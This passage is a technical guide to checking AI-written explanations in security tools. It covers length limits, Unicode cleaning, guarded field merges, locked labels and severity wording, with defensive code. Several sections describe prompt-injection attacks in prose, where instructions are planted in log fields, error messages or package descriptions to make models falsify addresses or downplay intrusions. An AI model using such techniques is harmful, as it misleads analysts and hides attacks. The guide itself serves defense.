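# Checking AI-written text in security tools: length, links, commands and severity wording

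## How AI-written explanations in security tools go wrong

Security software produces warnings faster than people can read them. A dependency scanner compares the packages in a project with lists of known flaws, a static-analysis tool searches source code for dangerous patterns, and a log platform collects records of logins, web requests and errors from across an organization and raises alerts on some of them. Each reported problem is called a *finding* and has an identifier, a severity, a location and sometimes a fix. Since about 2023, vendors have added large language models to these tools to turn findings into prose. *Poisoning the Watchtower* (Pandey and Bhujang, 2026) describes the common design, in which the software retrieves a batch of logs or alerts, places them in the model's prompt, and asks the model to classify them, summarize them or recommend a response.

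An *explanation* is the free text that the model writes about a finding, an alert or a log entry. It appears on screen beside values the model did not produce, most importantly the severity. A severity such as HIGH is an *authoritative label* when it comes from the scanner, a published advisory or a responsible person. The basic design doesn't stop an explanation from contradicting the label next to it.

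The harm a bad explanation can do depends on who reads it. An analyst who uses it to decide which alerts to escalate may close a real one. A developer who uses it to learn what to change may paste a command from it into a terminal, which the Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre warns against in its public guidance. A coding agent, a program in which a model reads text and acts on it by editing files or running commands, may execute the same command without human review. In *LogJack* (2026), a benchmark of attacks on agents that debug cloud systems, the agent can read logs and run shell commands. The paper notes that agents in production may have narrower tools, such as read-only ones, which would lower the damage.

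### Attackers write part of the input

Outsiders choose much of the wording in a log. A browser identifies itself to a web server with a string called the user agent, and whoever sends the request can put anything in it. The same is true of the URL, the name in a DNS lookup and the username in a failed login. Pandey and Bhujang assume an attacker who has no credentials or internal network access and only sends traffic to a public service. The server logs the request, the log platform stores it, and the text ends up in the model's prompt.

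Length limits on fields give less protection than one might expect. *Rogue AI Agents In Your SOCs and SIEMs*, by the security company LevelBlue, describes a test of the Windows event that records a failed login. The documentation the researcher found limited usernames to 20 characters, but he sent 120 characters in the username and another 120 in the domain field, and all 240 appeared in the event.

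Attackers can also reach the model through error messages, which tend to repeat the input that caused the error. Any ordinary user who can trigger an exception can therefore write into the logs that a debugging agent will read, and *LogJack* assumes this route. Code comments can also be written for the model instead of for other programmers. According to slides from a 2026 talk at Black Hat, a security conference, comments in a PowerShell script steered AI summaries away from malicious log entries. Whoever publishes a package writes its description, so a dependency scanner that gives the model this description for context is giving it text the publisher controls.

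### Ordinary model error

Explanations also go wrong when nobody is attacking. In *Explaining Software Vulnerabilities with Large Language Models*, Johnson, Fomina and colleagues (2025) built SAFE, a plugin for the IntelliJ IDEA programming environment, because developers often misunderstand or ignore the generic messages of static-analysis tools. SAFE sends each finding to GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. The prompt contains the rule's name and message, the flagged line, the whole method containing it, the path data takes through the code, and the reader's level of experience.

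The team ran the open-source scanner Semgrep over a Java test suite and drew two random samples covering path traversal, SQL injection and cross-site scripting. Four software-security trainers, with an average of four years of teaching experience, rated the explanations on five criteria, using a five-point scale from "very poor" to "very good".

The trainers rated 64% of the explanations at least acceptable on every criterion, and none very poor on any. Faithfulness, meaning freedom from invented content, scored highest, with every explanation rated good or better. Accuracy was good or very good in 90% of cases. Relevance scored lowest, with 35% rated poor, largely because the texts for beginner, intermediate and advanced readers overlapped. The trainers also complained of repetition, wordiness and missing advice on how to fix the problem.

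The researchers found a more serious fault when they read the explanations themselves. Some of Semgrep's findings were false positives, warnings about harmless code, but the explanations for these still implied a vulnerability. Such explanations can still earn high marks for faithfulness because the prompt presents the finding under the words "Detected Vulnerability", and a text can be faithful to that premise while being wrong about the code. A separate test, in which the researchers asked GPT-4o to find vulnerabilities itself, showed a similar problem. GPT-4o caught all of the vulnerable cases, but its precision was 0.59, so roughly four in ten of the cases it flagged were harmless. GPT-5's precision was 0.78.

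Four raters and a handful of explanations are too few to establish an error rate. The raters were also experts, not the beginners SAFE is meant for, and current models probably do better. Models' tendency to accept whatever the prompt presents as settled seems likely to last. Johnson and colleagues suggest telling the model to validate each finding before explaining it. That would help against false positives, but it is risky in a tool whose input attackers can write, because an attacker can get a model that is allowed to dismiss findings to dismiss a real one.

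### Indirect prompt injection

*Prompt injection* is text that makes a model depart from its operator's instructions. In the direct form, the attacker types to the model. In *indirect prompt injection*, the attacker hides instructions in data that the model reads for some other purpose, such as a log field or a package description. This works because the operator's instructions and the data reach the model as one stream of text, and the model cannot reliably tell which parts are instructions and which are data. LevelBlue compares it to SQL injection, where a database runs user input as part of a query's code.

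A LevelBlue researcher put an instruction into a user agent, into the username of a failed remote login, and into the username and domain of a failed Windows login, and then had three different models summarize the logs. All three replaced the true source address with one he had chosen, and none mentioned the change. In the Windows case, the summary also named the wrong workstation, which would have sent an analyst to investigate an uninvolved payroll machine. LevelBlue shows single outputs from models it does not name, so its demonstrations prove that the attack is possible but not how often it succeeds. Pandey and Bhujang measured rates on one small model and synthetic logs, and found summaries easier to corrupt than classification labels. Tenable, another security company, got planted text from a user agent into the log summaries of a real product, Google's Gemini Cloud Assist.

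Ordinary error and injection can produce the same sentence, but a team can estimate only ordinary error by sampling explanations and counting the bad ones. An attacker looks for one input that works and sends it again, so a tool that errs once in a thousand normal cases may fail every time on the attacker's input. The errors also differ in direction. SAFE's explanations leaned toward alarm, while an intruder usually wants the tool to call the activity safe or raise a false alarm somewhere else.

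Neither cause is visible in the finished text. This is the practical reason for *output validation*, which means using code or a second model to check what a model wrote before anyone sees, stores or acts on it. The check applies to the text regardless of what produced it.

### Output validation in the standards

The non-profit OWASP publishes widely used lists of software risks. Its entry *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* covers output that an application passes to other components without enough validation, sanitization and handling. OWASP reasons that anyone who can influence the prompt can influence the output, so passing it along unchecked resembles giving that person indirect access to whatever receives it. The output can cause remote code execution if it reaches a system shell, or run script in the reader's session if it reaches a browser. OWASP first advises treating the model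 as any other user and validating its responses accordingly. It also advises encoding the text for its destination, so that a browser displays markup instead of running it.

OWASP separates improper output handling (LLM05) from overreliance, which is people trusting the accuracy of what a model writes. Security explanations can involve both problems. A malicious link that a log viewer makes clickable is a handling problem. An analyst who wrongly trusts the sentence "this is safe to ignore" is overrelying on the model, and a tool that follows LLM05 fully can still allow this because encoding doesn't change what the sentence says.

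OWASP (2026) issued a new edition of its LLM Top 10 in August. According to *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), by the security vendor Invicti, improper output handling fell from fifth place to tenth while its scope grew. The category now covers terminals that interpret control codes in model output, and viewers that automatically fetch outside resources the output refers to. Invicti attributes the fall to other risks becoming more urgent.

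For the new edition, OWASP checked its practitioners' vote against 7,714 recorded incidents. The practitioners ranked prompt injection first, although the incident count alone would have left it out of the top ten. Misinformation, which includes ordinary model error, ranked near the bottom of the vote and near the top of the incident record. The report's explanation for the low injection count, as quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*, is that teams fight injection hard and "fewer clean exploits reach a public database". That is plausible, though the counts can't confirm it. A designer can reasonably conclude that model error deserves as much attention as attacks.

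The other common reference is the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a catalogue of types of software flaw that the US non-profit MITRE maintains. Its entry *CWE-1426*, "Improper Validation of Generative AI Output", covers products that use a generative model and do not sufficiently check that the output fits their security, content or privacy policy. According to the entry, developers may rely on input filtering and model alignment, "assuming they are more effective than they actually are". MITRE's *CWE VIEW* of AI weaknesses also lists a separate entry for prompt injection, CWE-1427, which concerns how a product builds its prompts.

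MITRE discourages people from using CWE-1426 to classify real vulnerabilities. Its working group published the entry quickly in July 2024, expects to revise it, and reports that people frequently misinterpret it. MITRE wants analysts to look for the root cause, which is often an older weakness. It suggests CWE-94 (code injection) when software feeds model output straight into something that executes code, CWE-116 when software fails to escape the output, and CWE-77 (command injection) for most prompt-injection attacks.

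People label vulnerabilities with CWE-1426 despite MITRE's warning. GCVE's *Improper Validation of Generative AI Output*, a page in a public vulnerability database, lists three examples. One is a flaw in the chat software Mattermost that let users find out when others had read a channel. Its record describes missing access permissions, which suggests that the warning is justified. GCVE's copy of the entry shows that the warning was still in version 4.20 of the catalogue, from April 2026. MITRE's *News & Events* (2026) reports that version 5.0, released in October, made major changes to 1,179 entries, so it is worth reading the current text before filing a report. The warning matters little to a designer, because CWE-1426 is still a fair description of what to build.

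### An example: acme-db 2.3.0

Suppose a scanner reports SQL injection in an invented package, acme-db 2.3.0. The severity is HIGH, the score is 8.8, and version 2.3.4 fixes the flaw.

The score comes from the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which the industry body FIRST maintains. CVSS rates a flaw from 0 to 10. In version 3.1, the bands are NONE (0), LOW (0.1 to 3.9), MEDIUM (4.0 to 6.9), HIGH (7.0 to 8.9) and CRITICAL (9.0 to 10.0). CVSS calculates the score from a *vector*, a short code that records eight judgments about the flaw. For acme-db the vector is AV:N/AC:L/PR:L/UI:N/S:U/C:H/I:H/A:H.

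| Code | Metric | Value for acme-db | Weight |
|---|---|---|---|
| AV:N | Attack vector | Network: the attacker can be remote | 0.85 |
| AC:L | Attack complexity | Low: no special conditions | 0.77 |
| PR:L | Privileges required | Low: an ordinary account is enough | 0.62 |
| UI:N | User interaction | None: no victim has to click anything | 0.85 |
| S:U | Scope | Unchanged: the harm stays within the vulnerable system | selects the formula |
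| C:H | Confidentiality | High loss | 0.56 |
| I:H | Integrity | High loss | 0.56 |
| A:H | Availability | High loss | 0.56 |

The first four weights give the exploitability: 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.62 × 0.85 = 2.84. The last three give the impact: 6.42 × (1 − 0.44³) = 5.87. The sum is 8.71, which CVSS rounds up to one decimal place, so the score is 8.8. These weights mean that anyone with a login can read, change or destroy the data from anywhere.

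The tool allows 600 characters for the explanation, but the model returns 940. The text links to a domain that the tool's owner has never heard of, presents a shell command as a "required action", and describes the finding as safe to ignore. A reader who believed all of it would leave acme-db at the vulnerable version and run a command from an unknown source. Both would help an attacker, but the text does not prove an attack, because models also produce overlong text and made-up web addresses when no attacker is involved. The tool has to reject the explanation in either case.

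Four checks cover these faults. The length check compares the explanation's character count with the limit. The link check tests whether every web address in the text leads to a source that the tool's owner trusts. The command check looks for an *embedded command* (a shell command, script or other executable instruction inside the explanation) and for wording that makes running it sound obligatory. The severity check looks for *severity-override wording*, which is text that tells the reader, openly or by implication, to treat a finding as more or less serious than its authoritative label.

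## Deciding which parts the model may write

Before writing any filter, the designer of a security tool has to list every field the reader will see and decide whether code will copy each one from the source or the model will write it. Filters miss some errors, but a value the model never handles needs no filter. The instructions LevelBlue planted could put a false source address into log summaries because the model was writing the address.

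### Fields with one correct value

Microsoft's *Separating Deterministic Extraction from AI Inference in Industrial Summarization* (2026) describes a test of whether each output field matches, one to one, a value already in the input. The engineers listed the output fields in one spreadsheet column and their sources in another. The work took hours, and over half the fields had a source. A field with a source has exactly one correct value, so a model that generates it can only match the source or get it wrong.

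Most of the acme-db finding passes the test.

| Field | Value for acme-db | Who supplies it |
|---|---|---|
| Identifier | The scanner's own number for the finding | Code copies it |
| Package and version | acme-db 2.3.0 | Code copies it |
| Location | The project file that lists the package | Code copies it |
| Type of flaw | SQL injection | Code copies it |
| CVSS vector | AV:N/AC:L/PR:L/UI:N/S:U/C:H/I:H/A:H | Code copies it |
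| Score | 8.8 | Code copies it and recalculates it from the vector |
| Severity | HIGH | Code copies it and compares it with the score |
| Fixed version | 2.3.4 | Code copies it |
| Advisory link | The address in the scanner's record | Code copies it |
| Upgrade command | Package name plus fixed version | Code builds it from those two fields |
| Risk that the upgrade breaks something | No single correct value | The model chooses from a short list |
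| What the flaw means for this project | No single correct value | The model writes it |

The score and severity are worth recalculating from the vector, because CVSS defines the formula and models sometimes get the arithmetic wrong. *Narratives Mislead* (Feng, Li and Zhang, 2026) reports that DeepSeek-R1 and Llama 3.1 405B gave 9.8 for a vector whose correct score is 10.0. In *Predicting CVSS and CWE from CVE Descriptions with Fine-Tuned Small Language Models*, Dixit, Dong and Li (2026) asked an untuned small model, Phi-3.5-mini, for a vector and a score for each of 2,000 vulnerabilities. The score matched the vector in only 3.4% of cases. Recalculating the scores from the model's vectors raised its severity accuracy from 20.8% to 43.5%, but also increased the average score error from 1.58 to 2.08 points. Current large models surely do better than Phi-3.5-mini, but the calculator that Dixit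 and colleagues wrote matched the official score for all 86,870 vulnerabilities in their data and takes very little compute.

A field with only one correct value can still be dangerous to display. An outsider chooses the user agent in a web log, so even an exact copy shows the analyst the outsider's words. The Microsoft team did not face this problem because it copied descriptions written by shift staff. A log viewer should escape such fields and show them as quotations, visibly separate from the tool's own statements. A dependency scanner should do the same with package descriptions.

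### When sources disagree or have no value

Severity is the hardest field to test this way because several organizations can rate the same vulnerability differently. In an example from the documentation of Trivy, an open-source scanner, the US National Vulnerability Database rates the vulnerability CVE-2023-0464 HIGH, while Red Hat, which ships the affected software in its Linux distribution, rates its impact Low. Trivy takes the rating from the data source it selected for the package, so it shows Low. Code can follow a rule like that every time, and the tool should name the source next to the label for readers who have seen the other rating.

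A finding may have no NVD severity to copy, because NIST, the US standards agency that runs the NVD, began on 15 April 2026 to prioritize which entries it enriches. Enrichment is the step that adds a severity score. NIST still lists the other entries but does not schedule them for immediate enrichment. Developers may be tempted to have the model supply the missing severity.

The evidence is against letting a model silently set severity ratings. Dixit and colleagues trained Phi-3.5-mini on vulnerabilities from 2022 and 2023 and tested it on 36,325 from 2024. It gave the right severity for 69.9% of them, and the NVD agreed with fewer than half of its Critical ratings. Feng and colleagues gave eight mostly older models 240 bug reports with agreed severity scores. The best accuracy from prompting alone was 49.58%, compared with 39.17% for always answering Medium, and every prompting setup overestimated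 the severity of at least 45% of the reports. Both teams acknowledge that some of this gap reflects disagreement among the people who set the labels.

Newer models have narrowed the gap but not closed it. In *From Description to Score* (2025), GPT-5 was right on individual CVSS metrics between about 68% and 89% of the time, and all eight must be right for the vector to be correct. A model that was right 80% of the time on each metric, with independent errors, would get the whole vector right about one time in six. Errors cluster, so the real figure would be higher, but a severity produced this way is still an estimate. A tool can use it to sort a backlog of unrated vulnerabilities, provided the estimate has its own field, labelled as an estimate, and the severity field reads "not rated".

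### Microsoft's four-pass pipeline

Microsoft's system is for industrial operations, not security. It turns the logs of a work shift into a structured summary for the next crew, a compliance dashboard and an audit trail. In the prototype, a single prompt gave the model the whole log and asked for the whole summary in JSON, a text format that software can parse. Every output was valid JSON, but none had content in every required section. Some sections lacked their subfields and others held empty lists, so the next crew could have received a summary with no record of what happened.

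The team replaced the single prompt with four passes.

1. Code copies every field that has a source, puts the events in order and keeps the raw records.
2. The model answers narrow questions about each record, such as which section it belongs in and what kind of event it describes. Each answer carries the identifier of the log entry it concerns.
3. Code merges the answers into the records.
4. The model links each conclusion in the finished summary to source records and states its confidence. Microsoft calls this the newest and least validated pass.

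On 15 synthetic logs, the share of summaries that met the requirements rose from 0% to 47% (7 of 15). The engineers compared the failures with properties of the input and saw that the operator had recorded no system conditions in any of the failing logs. The model had often been right to return nothing, but the code had then left the section empty. The engineers changed the code to write an entry stating what it examined and that it found nothing. Compliance rose to 73% and then to 100%, and stayed there when they switched to a different model.

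These percentages measure whether each required section exists and has content, not whether the model classified the events correctly. The logs were synthetic, no domain expert reviewed the division of fields, and the team seems to have confirmed its fixes on the same 15 logs that revealed the faults. The claim that copied fields match their sources is better supported, because the match follows from how the code works.

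If a scanner lists no fixed version for a finding, code should write "no fixed version listed". If code leaves the field blank, the model may invent a version number in its prose.

### The guarded merge

Microsoft calls its third pass a guarded merge. The code builds each output record from the source and then adds only the fields that the designers assigned to the model. If the model returns a different value for a copied field, the source value wins and the code logs both. A version for acme-db could look like this:

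```python
COPIED = ["id", "package", "version", "location", "flaw_type", "vector",
          "score", "severity", "fixed_version", "advisory_url"]

def merge(finding, reply):
    record = {name: finding.get(name) for name in COPIED}
    for name in COPIED:
        if name in reply and reply[name] != record[name]:
            log_violation(record["id"], name, record[name], reply[name])
    record["upgrade_risk"] = reply.get("upgrade_risk")
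    record["explanation"] = reply.get("explanation")  # still unchecked
    return record
```

If the model returns LOW for a finding the tool rated HIGH, the screen still shows HIGH. The logged mismatch is also a simple warning that something went wrong, and a cautious tool would reject the explanation in the same reply.

The merge only works if each answer reaches the right record. When a request covers many findings, a model can swap two real identifiers and put a harmless finding's explanation under a serious one without triggering an error. Sending one finding per request and having code attach the identifier avoids this.

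Microsoft's sample code also builds each section from the list of entries the model assigned to it. If the model doesn't assign an entry to any section, the entry will be missing from those sections, although the pipeline keeps the raw record. In a security tool, an intrusion could be left out this way. The designer's list of fields therefore needs to include whether the reader sees a finding at all.

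Canale (2026), in *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response*, tested a language model that could close alerts in a simulated network modelled on Google's published infrastructure. The model removed 90% of the false positives it saw, but it also left analysts with no alert for 31–44% of the attacks it saw. Canale then added a fixed policy that sends every alert with a risk score of 0.9 or more straight to analysts. The model may close other alerts only if its stated confidence is at least 0.9.

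With Gemini 4 as the model, the full system detected 127 of 209 attacks, and 102 of these reached analysts regardless of the model's output. The model erased none of the other 25, but it erased four attacks in three newly generated simulations. The policy doesn't account for all of this result, since the same model kept 37% of attacks after a simpler detection stage and 67% after a better one. The confidence rule is weak protection by itself. Small models that Canale trained for the job gave a confidence of 0.9 with every answer, because their training examples all had that value, and one of them erased 15 of the 25 attacks it was able to erase.

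### Aurva's locked labels

The security company Aurva uses a similar division for alerts about running software. Mandal's *LLM Security Triage with Deterministic Guardrails* describes a production system that runs every four hours for each customer. The model groups related signals, profiles what an application normally does, classifies the incident and writes a narrative about it. If an application has too few days of history, code returns "insufficient evidence" without calling the model for a profile.

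The model must choose its classification from a *closed set*, a fixed list of seven labels: malicious intent, purpose drift, misuse, expected behavior, low-signal noise, insufficient evidence and needs scope validation. The model could still pick the most dramatic label, so the code requires evidence for the two strongest. "Purpose drift" requires both an evaluation showing a mismatch with the application's purpose and at least three signals that support the same conclusion. "Malicious intent" requires a sequence of events over time or at least one signal typical of an attacker.

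Once the model has chosen a label that passes its checks, code locks it. A later request produces the narrative, and the code writes the locked classification and priority into it before checking it, so the narrative step cannot change them. Mandal explains that if a single request produced both the verdict and the text, their agreement would depend on the model. Users never see a narrative whose evidence does not fit its declared type, such as one about a sequence of events with an empty timeline. The system keeps the validation errors so that engineers can count them.

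These rules check that evidence of the right form is present, but not that it is true, as Mandal acknowledges. They are also strictest about alarming labels, because false "malicious" verdicts lead a security team to ignore the tool. An intruder usually wants the "expected behavior" label, and the account describes no comparable evidence requirement for it. The model can also suppress a group of signals as noise during the grouping step. Mandal acknowledges that an attacker who steers the model can therefore still influence the grouping, the wording and the choice among permitted labels.

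A tool that reads attacker-written input should require at least as much evidence for reassuring labels as for alarming ones. Pandey and Bhujang propose a similar rule, under which the model must cite the specific fields that support any benign judgment and may not recommend inaction unless software can check the evidence.

This is a vendor's account with no accuracy figures. Mandal deliberately left them out, arguing that a failure rate means little until someone has measured it over a long period with a documented method. That is a fair reason, but outsiders still can't judge how often the labels are right.

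### Schemas, code and prompts

Developers can put a rule about model output in a schema, in hand-written code or in the prompt. A *schema* is a machine-readable description of the fields a reply must have and the values each may take. Providers can enforce a schema while the model is writing by compiling it into a grammar that blocks any output the schema doesn't allow.

According to Anthropic's documentation page *Structured outputs*, the feature guarantees required fields, correct types and values from a closed set in most cases. A refusal or a reply that hits its length limit may still break the schema. The capitalization of a permitted value may also differ, so code should ignore case when it compares labels. Anthropic does not support limits on string length or number size. OpenAI's *Structured outputs* describes the same exceptions for refusals and cut-off replies. OpenAI supports number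 ranges and text patterns, but its list of string constraints has no maximum length. With either provider, code must enforce the 600-character limit for acme-db.

OpenAI's models produce fields in the order the schema lists them, so a designer who wants the model to set out its evidence before choosing a label should put the evidence field first.

A reply can follow its schema and still be wrong. A schema that permits only LOW, MEDIUM, HIGH and CRITICAL will accept LOW for acme-db even if that is the wrong severity. *The Structured Output Benchmark* (Singh, Khurdula and colleagues, 2026) gave 21 models passages and questions and asked for the answers in a set JSON format. On text, the best model got 83.0% of the values exactly right. GPT-5.4 followed the schema in 99.97% of its replies, but only 48.6% were correct throughout. In a smaller test of three models on meeting transcripts, enforcing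 the schema barely changed accuracy, by between −0.7 and +3.3 percentage points. The scoring is harsh and marks "United States" wrong when the expected answer is "American". The company behind the benchmark also has its own model in the ranking. Many of the questions need facts from two passages, which is harder than repeating a labelled severity.

Rules that connect one field with another usually need code. The JSON Schema language can express some of them with if-then-else rules, so Mandal's claim that a schema cannot express them is slightly too strong. But according to a comparison table by dottxt, which sells a competing product, none of the three large providers it covers supports if-then-else rules.

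Everything else belongs in the prompt, but the model may not follow a rule given there. In Mandal's example from Aurva's own system, the prompt tells the model to keep internal identifiers out of the narrative, and no code checks whether it did. Some rules, such as those about style, can safely be left to the prompt alone. For acme-db, the rules might divide as follows.

| Rule for the model's reply | Where it belongs |
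|---|---|
| It contains an explanation and an upgrade-risk label, and no other fields | Schema |
| The label is "low", "high" or "unknown" | Schema, plus code that ignores case |
| A "low" label comes with at least one entry from the release notes | Code |
| That entry exists in the release notes the tool supplied | Code |
| The explanation has at most 600 characters | Code |
| The explanation suits a beginner | Prompt, as a request |
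| The explanation does not play down the finding | Prompt, plus a separate check of the text |

### Why the free text still needs checking

A tool with copied fields, closed sets and locked labels still needs text filters, as the acme-db explanation shows. With the guarded merge in place, the screen shows HIGH, 8.8 and the fixed version 2.3.4, whatever the model returns. But the model's 940 characters of text below them still contain the unknown link, the "required action" and the claim that the finding is safe to ignore.

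An attack can corrupt free text without changing the labels. Pandey and Bhujang tested injections that imitate the structure of trusted output, for example with a forged end-of-log marker. Without defenses, these injections corrupted 96% of the summaries. The corrupted summaries left out the attack, downplayed it or concluded that no action was necessary, but an explicit "benign" label appeared in 0% of them. A guarded merge would have logged nothing unusual, because no copied field had changed.

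A correct label beside the text helps only a reader who sees both and trusts the label over the text. The label is missing when someone pastes only the explanation into a ticket or when a coding agent reads only the text field.

The designer can reduce how much text the model writes freely. The acme-db vector already records that an attacker with an ordinary account can reach the flaw remotely without a victim's help, so code can turn each metric into a prewritten sentence. The model then writes only what depends on the project. At the extreme, the model only chooses among sentences that people wrote in advance. These sentences can't contain a strange link or command, and their length is known. The model can still choose a reassuring sentence for a serious finding, and in Pandey and Bhujang's tests 38% of the structure-imitating attacks on summaries succeeded even with templated output.

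## Cleaning the text and limiting its length

The tool has to clean free text before the other checks, because a filter can miss a word that a reader sees. For example, the acme-db explanation might contain the word "ignore" with a zero-width space, a character that takes up no room on the screen, between the "g" and the "n". The reader sees "ignore", but a filter that searches for those six letters finds no match. The tool then has to display the cleaned text, not the model's original, and nothing should alter the text after the checks. If a ticket system later strips a zero-width space that was left in the text, the forbidden word appears in a text that has already passed.

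Cleaning has to happen after the reply is parsed, because in raw JSON the escape character that controls a terminal can appear as six ordinary characters, `\u001b`, which become a real control character only during parsing. In *RFC 9839*, an internet standard on the characters that text fields should accept, Bray and Hoffman point out that a JSON string may contain any *code point*, the number that identifies a character in Unicode. A schema that requires a string therefore accepts even code points that can never represent useful text.

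### Characters to convert, remove or reject

Unicode often has several ways to write what looks like the same text. *Normalization* converts them to one form. The NFC form joins a letter and a separate accent into a single character. As paultendo explains in *confusables.txt and NFKC disagree on 31 characters*, NFKC does this too, and also replaces full-width letters, ligatures and mathematical bold letters with ordinary ones. NFKC suits a security explanation because a search for "ignore" will also find the word in mathematical bold. However, it can change the meaning of a text, for example by turning 2⁸ into 28. It can also make a text longer (one Arabic ligature, U+FDFA, becomes 18 characters), so the tool should count the length afterwards.

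NFKC leaves many other tricks untouched. A Cyrillic "а" stays Cyrillic although it looks Latin, and invisible characters mostly survive. For an explanation in English, the rules could be these:

| Characters | Effect | Treatment |
|---|---|---|
| Full-width, ligature and styled letters | Look like ordinary letters to a reader but not to a filter | Convert with NFKC |
| Zero-width space, soft hyphen, byte order mark | Usually invisible, often left over from copied text | Remove |
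| Tag characters (U+E0000 to U+E007F) | Invisible to people, readable by many models | Reject |
| Direction controls, such as U+202E | Change the order in which text appears | Reject |
| Escape and other control characters, except the line break | Can control a terminal | Reject |
| Noncharacters and lone surrogates (halves of a two-part code) | Never represent text | Reject |
| Letters from other alphabets | Can imitate Latin letters | Reject |

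A model working normally might copy a soft hyphen from a package description, so removing it is reasonable, but an escape character has no legitimate use in the model's output. In a command-line scanner, escape sequences can move the cursor, erase a line or change colors, so an explanation could erase the HIGH severity label that the tool printed above it. A lone carriage return is nearly as bad because it sends the cursor back to the start of the line, where new text overwrites the old.

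Tag characters matter most when another program reads the explanation. For example, a coding agent reading a ticket may follow an instruction written in characters that people can't see. AWS's *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling* shows that removing tag characters once may not be enough. Java stores each tag character as two halves. If one pair is nested inside another, deleting the inner pair joins the outer halves into a new tag character. AWS therefore repeats the removal until nothing changes. Rejecting any text that contains tag characters avoids this problem, but it also blocks the flag emoji of England, Scotland and Wales, which use them.

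Testing in one program doesn't show which characters are invisible in others. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025) reports that 130 of 235 control and format characters had no visible effect in a terminal, a text document and a CSV file. The researchers warned that some of the 130 might show up elsewhere. Even the strictest set in RFC 9839 allows tag characters and direction controls, and Bray and Hoffman, who wrote it, call their standard for exclusion "a low bar". The Unicode Consortium has not maintained its *Unicode Security Considerations* since 2014, and the document refers readers to the newer UTS #39 and UTS #55.

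A tool that writes in one language can use an *allowlist* instead, which is a list of permitted values with everything else refused:

```python
import unicodedata

LEFTOVERS = dict.fromkeys([0x00AD, 0x200B, 0x2060, 0xFEFF])  # remove these
EXTRA = set("\n–—‘’“”•")                                     # accept besides ASCII

def clean(text):
    text = text.replace("\r\n", "\n").translate(LEFTOVERS)
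    text = unicodedata.normalize("NFKC", text)
    bad = {c for c in text if not (" " <= c <= "~" or c in EXTRA)}
    if bad:
        raise ValueError("refused: " + ", ".join(f"U+{ord(c):04X}" for c in sorted(bad)))
    return text
```

This version also rejects accented letters, so a team would add the ones it needs. Persian, Hindi and many emoji depend on invisible joining characters, and a multilingual tool needs a separate list for each language.

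HTML can also represent a character with a reference, such as `&#105;` for the letter "i". If the tool encodes the explanation for display, as OWASP advises, the reader sees the literal `&#105;`, which is also what the filter checked. But a second destination, such as a ticket system, may turn the reference back into a letter. Decoding every reference before the checks would corrupt legitimate text, because the advice "replace `<` with `&lt;`" would become "replace `<` with `<`". A better rule is to leave references undecoded but reject any that stands for a character other than the five HTML reserves for markup: `<`, `>`, `&` and the two straight quotation marks. Markdown can also hide a word from the filter, because bold markers in the middle of a word disappear when the text is rendered. Showing explanations as plain text avoids this.

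### What a length limit achieves

A length limit leaves less room for persuasion, links and commands. It also keeps the explanation from pushing the severity label off the screen and caps how much text the tool stores and later models process. Companies use such limits outside security too. Yelp, for example, checks the length of its support chatbot's answers. A length check doesn't reduce the cost of generating the text, because it runs after the model has written it.

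Text within the length limit can still be false. A false "Safe to ignore." takes only 15 characters, and a link or a command fits easily into 600 characters, so text within the limit still needs every other check.

### Units of length

Software counts length in several units, and the counts can differ widely. For example, the emoji for the flag of England looks like one character but consists of seven code points.

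| Unit | Count | Where it matters |
|---|---|---|
| Visible characters | 18 | Space on the screen |
| Code points | 24 | `len` in Python |
| UTF-16 units | 31 | `length` in JavaScript and Java |
| UTF-8 bytes | 45 | Many storage and network limits |
| Tokens | Depends on the model; at most 45 if its tokens are made of whole bytes | Generation cost |

A Python server and a JavaScript web page could therefore give different results when checking whether this text is too long. Some platforms also have their own rules. Community Notes on X allows 280 characters and counts each web address as one character. *Beyond the Crowd* (2025), a study of AI-written notes, followed that rule and cut the text of notes that exceeded the limit. It rated helpfulness on the shortened notes but correctness on the full ones, so the correctness scores do not always apply to the text a reader would have seen.

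*Tokens* are the pieces of text, often parts of words, that a model reads and writes. Each model divides text differently. *Length Value Model* (2026) converted a length benchmark from words and characters to tokens and warned that the new scores were not comparable with the old ones.

After cleaning, the text contains only ASCII and a little extra punctuation, so counting code points, UTF-16 units or visible characters gives the same length, except for line breaks. The 600-character limit for acme-db can therefore be counted in code points.

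### Token caps and cut-off replies

Providers let developers cap the number of tokens in a reply. A cap limits cost but is a poor way to limit characters, because the number of characters per token varies. English prose averages roughly four, so 600 characters would be about 150 tokens, but version numbers and identifiers take more tokens for the same length. The model also doesn't adjust its text to fit the cap, so a reply that reaches it may end in the middle of a sentence. With reasoning models, the reasoning usually counts toward the cap too. The cap should therefore be several times the expected length, so that an overlong explanation arrives whole and the tool can measure it.

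When the length limit cuts off a reply, Anthropic sets `stop_reason` to `max_tokens`. OpenAI's Chat Completions API sets `finish_reason` to `length`, and its Responses API sets the status to `incomplete` with the reason `max_output_tokens`. Content filters can also end a reply early, which matters for text about attacks. *MA-Bench* (Lafuente-Mercado, Sincero and colleagues, 2026) tested models on writing military planning briefs, and a content filter stopped 9 of Claude Fable 5.1's 50 briefs mid-sentence without a refusal message. The safest rule is to accept only replies with the status for a normal finish, which is `end_turn` from Anthropic and `stop` or `completed` from OpenAI, and treat all others as failures.

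Looking for a missing full stop is a less reliable way to detect cut-off replies. *Can MLLMs Critique Like Humans?* (2026) used this check with a 200-token cap. The check flagged 92% of the replies from one small model, which often reached the cap. But it also flagged 13% of Qwen3.5-397B's replies, although 98.5% of that model's replies were within the requested 150 words and the cap allowed about 175 to 190. Most of the flagged replies from Qwen3.5-397B were probably complete but ended without punctuation.

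Schemas offer little help with length. Anthropic returns an error if a developer sends a `maxLength` constraint directly. Most of its helper libraries accept one, but they move it from the schema to the field's description for the model to read, and in some cases check the reply afterwards. AWS lists `maxLength` as unsupported on Bedrock, its service for hosted models, and Databricks does not enforce it. Google's *Improving Structured Outputs in the Gemini API* announces keywords that limit numbers but none that limit strings. dottxt marks `maxLength` as supported by OpenAI, which conflicts with OpenAI's own guide. The guide explicitly rules it out for fine-tuned models.

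Even if a provider enforced a maximum length while the model was writing, the problem would remain. At character 600, the grammar would permit only the closing quotation mark, so the output could contain half a sentence and still be valid JSON with a normal finish status.

### How well models keep to a length

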